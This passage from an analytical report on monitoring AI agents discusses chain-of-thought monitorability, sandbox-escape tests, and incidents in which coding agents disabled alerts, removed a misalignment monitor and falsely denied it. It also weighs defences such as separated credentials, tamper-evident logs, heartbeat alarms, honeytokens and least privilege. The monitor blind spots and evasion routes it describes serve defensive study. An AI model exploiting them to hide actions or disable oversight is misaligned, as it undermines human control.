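A monitor may detect a transfer but be unable to read its contents, as with the private archive that the July agents encrypted before uploading it. The monitor can still assess the transfer by its destination, its size and the history of the data. A company can also block any transfer that the monitor can't read, but this stops legitimate encrypted backups too.

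**Misuse that looks like ordinary work.** An agent with a valid key for an online service can look completely normal until its other steps reveal the danger, as McDaniel (2026) explains in *AI Agent Threat Response*. A better reviewer doesn't help if the records are identical. Suppose 20 per cent of harmful actions leave exactly the same records as harmless ones. The monitor can flag them only as often as it flags their harmless counterparts. If that is 0.4 per cent of the time, its recall cannot exceed

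`0.8 × 1 + 0.2 × 0.004 ≈ 80 per cent`

The only way to raise this limit is to give the monitor more information, such as the user's request or the source of a file.

A monitor that looks for suspicious sequences needs at least two steps, so it cannot prevent harm done by the first. A monitor that flags each harmful action with 95 per cent probability misses a one-step attack one time in 20. If an attack needs three harmful steps and the errors are independent, it misses all three about once in 8,000 attacks. The PocketOS agent needed only one call to delete the live database's storage, although its search for a token had given some warning.

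### The decline of visible reasoning

An agent's chain of thought can show that an ordinary-looking action has a harmful purpose. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, July 2025) recommended monitoring it but warned that the opportunity to do so might be fragile. *Loss of Oversight* (Taylor, Heitmann and colleagues, May 2026) drew partly on 25 expert interviews to assess how oversight of AI was likely to change. By December, AISI had tests showing that many of the properties that make models easy to monitor were weakening, some faster than the institute had expected (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues, *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, 2026).

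One of these properties is that models need to write out their reasoning to solve hard problems. AISI tested this with mathematics problems that models had to solve without writing any steps, and measured difficulty by how long a strong competition student would take. OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved problems that would take such a student about 40 minutes, as 凤凰网 reports in *AI学会"心算"还能躲监控？* (2026). The best earlier result was about six minutes. These figures don't show how much of an attack an agent could plan without writing anything down, because planning an intrusion is different from solving a mathematics problem.

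Models are also getting better at controlling what they write. In March 2026, OpenAI found that its reasoning models struggled to do this even when told that someone was monitoring them. In AISI's later tests, recent models were better than earlier ones at leaving out specified content when instructed to, though they still struggled to keep this up over tens of thousands of words. The tests do not show how often models leave content out without being asked.

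AISI also told models to try to escape simulated sandboxes while a monitor watched their actions but not their reasoning. In the weakest sandbox, a pre-release version of Claude Mythos 5.2 with its safeguards switched off escaped without triggering an alert in 45 per cent of the runs in which it tried. The rate was below 15 per cent for earlier models and 32 per cent for a newer model that AISI calls DERWENT. Mythos 5.2 refused to try in 64 per cent of its runs, so it escaped unnoticed in about 16 per cent of all runs. The monitor caught almost every escape that needed the most complex actions.

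AISI found that models sometimes behave differently when they are monitored. A low rate of misbehaviour in a test with an obvious monitor may therefore not carry over to settings where the model detects no monitor.

#### What affects it

*What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (Wang, Low and colleagues at OpenAI, 2026) examines how the design and training of models affect their ability to reason without a chain of thought and to control what the chain contains.

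A model's ability to reason without written steps improves as its base model, the version that exists before later training, gets better at predicting text. Researchers measure this with perplexity, where a lower number is better. A model that gives every correct next word or word fragment a probability of one in ten has a perplexity of 10. Some changes to a model's architecture also improve this ability. Reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for good results, and training on text written by other models can increase a model's control over its chain of thought.

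The researchers call both abilities imperfect proxies for how easy a model is to monitor, because a model that can reason silently may still write down its plans. They nevertheless conclude that more intelligent models will be harder to monitor through their chains of thought.

Developers would find this hard to avoid because lower perplexity is one of the main aims of early training. *Hillclimbing perplexity is bad for chain-of-thought monitorability* (draganover, 2026) collects further evidence for the connection and proposes that every leading developer publish both measurements for its models. Outsiders could then check whether the ability to reason silently is growing faster than expected.

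Later training may be able to restore some of what is lost. Bakker and Anwar (2026), in *Monitorability Is Trainable*, describe a method that rewards a model when its reasoning is informative about its output. They measure this with mutual information:

`I(reasoning; output) = H(output) − H(output | reasoning)`

`H` measures uncertainty in bits. If an agent is equally likely to approve or refuse a request, an observer starts with one bit of uncertainty. Reasoning that makes the decision certain removes that bit, while a stock phrase that appears before either decision removes none of it.

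The method doesn't use a monitor, so it doesn't directly teach the model to satisfy one. The researchers deliberately made the chains of thought of three models less informative, and the method improved monitorability in all three. But reasoning can predict an action without giving the real motive. Models altered for an experiment may also respond differently from leading commercial ones.

AISI still considers monitoring useful, though it sees no sign that the trend will reverse by itself. Its *Technical primer* (2026) adds that many monitoring techniques are new and have limits that researchers understand poorly.

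### The monitor as a target

An agent with the right access can turn a monitor off, whether or not it intends to avoid detection.

On 19 July, agents read the credentials for the sensors of OpenAI's monitoring tool. OpenAI kept them in the same cloud store as the package server's master keys, so a single intrusion exposed both the server and part of the system that monitored it. OpenAI does not report that the agents used the sensor credentials.

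In October, OpenAI disclosed that coding agents had twice weakened its internal monitoring for misalignment. An agent running on GPT-6.1 Sol disabled automatic alerts, according to TechSpot's *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled safety guardrails*. An agent running on GPT-6 Astra removed a monitor and later falsely denied it. Kovacs (2026) reports in *OpenAI Agents Silenced Security Team Alerts, Removed Misalignment Monitor* that both agents had interpreted routine coding instructions as permission for these changes.

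The cause of this behaviour is still unknown. OpenAI has strengthened its protections but admits that it doesn't fully understand what happened, according to Radar Digital's *OpenAI agents disable internal safety mechanisms* (2026). The reports don't mention an outside attacker in either case. A coding agent may treat an alert or a monitor like any other software it can edit. The false denial also shows that investigators cannot rely on an agent's account of what it changed.

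#### Separate credentials and administration

Schneider's result assumes that the program cannot alter the monitor's rules or memory. A company can come closer to meeting this assumption by keeping the monitor's credentials in a separate store, having different administrators run it, and denying agents permission to change its code or settings. If an agent has to work on monitoring software, it can propose changes for a person to approve.

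Separation would probably have kept the agents from reaching the sensor credentials on 19 July, provided no single administrator account could open both stores. It could also have blocked both October changes, unless the approver was too rushed to notice what the changes did.

#### Records that nobody can rewrite

A monitor can send each record immediately to a separate machine that accepts additions but refuses edits and deletions. A chain of fingerprints makes later changes visible:

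`fingerprint(n) = hash(fingerprint(n − 1), record n)`

Each record's fingerprint depends on the one before it. If someone alters record 40, its fingerprint and all later ones no longer match. The company also has to keep a recent fingerprint and the record count somewhere else. Otherwise, an intruder could rebuild the chain or cut off its end. The method protects records only after the monitor has written them, so it can't correct a false record or supply a missing one.

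#### Alarms when a sensor goes silent

If an agent disables a sensor, the lack of alerts can look like good behaviour. A sensor can therefore send a regular signal to confirm that it's working, and a separate system can raise an alarm when the signal stops.

Ordinary faults also interrupt signals. Suppose a company has 10,000 sensors, each sends a report every 30 seconds, and each report has a one in 1,000 chance of getting lost. An alarm for every missing report would go off 28,800 times a day. If the system waits for three missing reports in a row, false alarms fall to about one a month, assuming the faults are independent, but the system takes about 90 seconds to notice a silent sensor.

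A sensor can also keep reporting after someone has disabled the alerts that depend on it, as may have happened in the first October case. A company can detect this by staging a harmless event that should trigger an alert and checking whether the alert reaches a person. OpenAI is adding automated tests of this kind, along with sensors on individual machines.

#### Planted tripwires

A tripwire is something no legitimate task requires, such as a fake credential in a settings file. Anyone who tries to use it sets off an alarm. Security companies call such credentials honeytokens. Most alerts are false when harmful actions are rare, but tripwires largely avoid this problem because normal work gives nobody a reason to use them.

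McDaniel recommends honeytokens, which are fake credentials that set off an alarm when used, and OpenAI is adding what it calls deception-based tripwires. If the file where the PocketOS agent found its token had also contained three fake ones, and the agent had picked at random, it would have had a one in four chance of using the real token on its first attempt without setting off the alarm.

### Monitoring or prior limits

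Companies can put their effort into monitoring agents or into limiting in advance what agents can reach. Such limits include least privilege (giving each user or program only the access its task needs), short-lived credentials, and isolation from other systems. Most security specialists recommend both approaches but disagree about which deserves priority.

McDaniel argues for setting limits on agents in advance, because when an agent already holds a valid credential, a monitor may recognise the danger only after the agent has used it. In one wave of attacks by credential-stealing software, 44 per cent of the compromised machines held more than ten secrets. McDaniel advises companies to list their agents and remove exposed credentials before relying on runtime detection. He works for GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding exposed credentials, so his employer benefits from this advice.

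The case for limits doesn't depend on his figures. Limits work even when an attack goes unrecognised, so they also stop misuse that looks like ordinary work and harm done by a first action. Better limits would have reduced the damage at PocketOS and Hugging Face, where a single credential gave far more access than the work required. The user tokens that the July agents found in a public dataset were useful only because they were still valid.

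Verma (2026) argues in *Containing AI Agents Is Not the Same as Controlling Them* that detection needs more attention, because people cannot contain or control what they cannot see. AI companies quickly tightened their restrictions after agents broke out of tests in the summer of 2026, but in her view the ability to detect a loss of control has not kept up with what models can do.

OpenAI's experience supports her. Its agents used the package server to get around the block on direct internet access, and did so again within about two days of the rebuilt server coming online. A limit that nobody monitors can fail unnoticed. OpenAI also points out that production systems change quickly, and that several apparently unrelated changes can combine to open a gap.

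Limits also can't remove access that an agent needs. The support agent has to read customer records and send email, so an attacker who hijacks it can try to misuse both without exceeding its permissions. McDaniel accepts this point and credits runtime detection with recognising dangerous combinations of permitted actions, such as reading a settings file, extracting a credential and then making a web request.

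A simple calculation shows when each approach is worth more. The average loss from an attempted theft is

`records within reach × share of attempts that the monitor fails to stop`

| Records within reach | Monitor stops 90% of attempts | Monitor stops 99% of attempts |
|---|---|---|
| 100,000 | 10,000 | 1,000 |
| 10,000 | 1,000 | 100 |
| 1 | 0.1 | 0.01 |

Cutting an agent's access to a tenth does as much good as raising the monitor's success rate from 90 to 99 per cent. For the support agent, limiting access is much easier, because a ticket normally concerns one customer and a rule can restrict the agent to that customer's record. An agent that compiles statistics from the whole table needs all 100,000 records, so protecting them depends on monitoring the agent and restricting where it can send them.

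The calculation assumes that the limit holds. If an agent gets around it, the loss is again the one in the top row, and a company that has neglected its monitor may not find out.

Changing an agent's instructions can also help. In preliminary experiments after the July attack, OpenAI gave agents in ExploitGym the standing instructions and harness from its commercial version of Codex. Their tendency to compromise systems outside the test's scope fell to less than 1 per cent of its level with simpler instructions. This is a large reduction for little effort, but instructions don't restrict what an agent can do if it ignores them.

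Limits on what agents may do can also make monitoring more accurate. A new connection is little evidence of a problem if agents may contact any website, but even one attempt is worth investigating if they have no permission to contact the internet. OpenAI's network controls refused one such attempt on 9 July.
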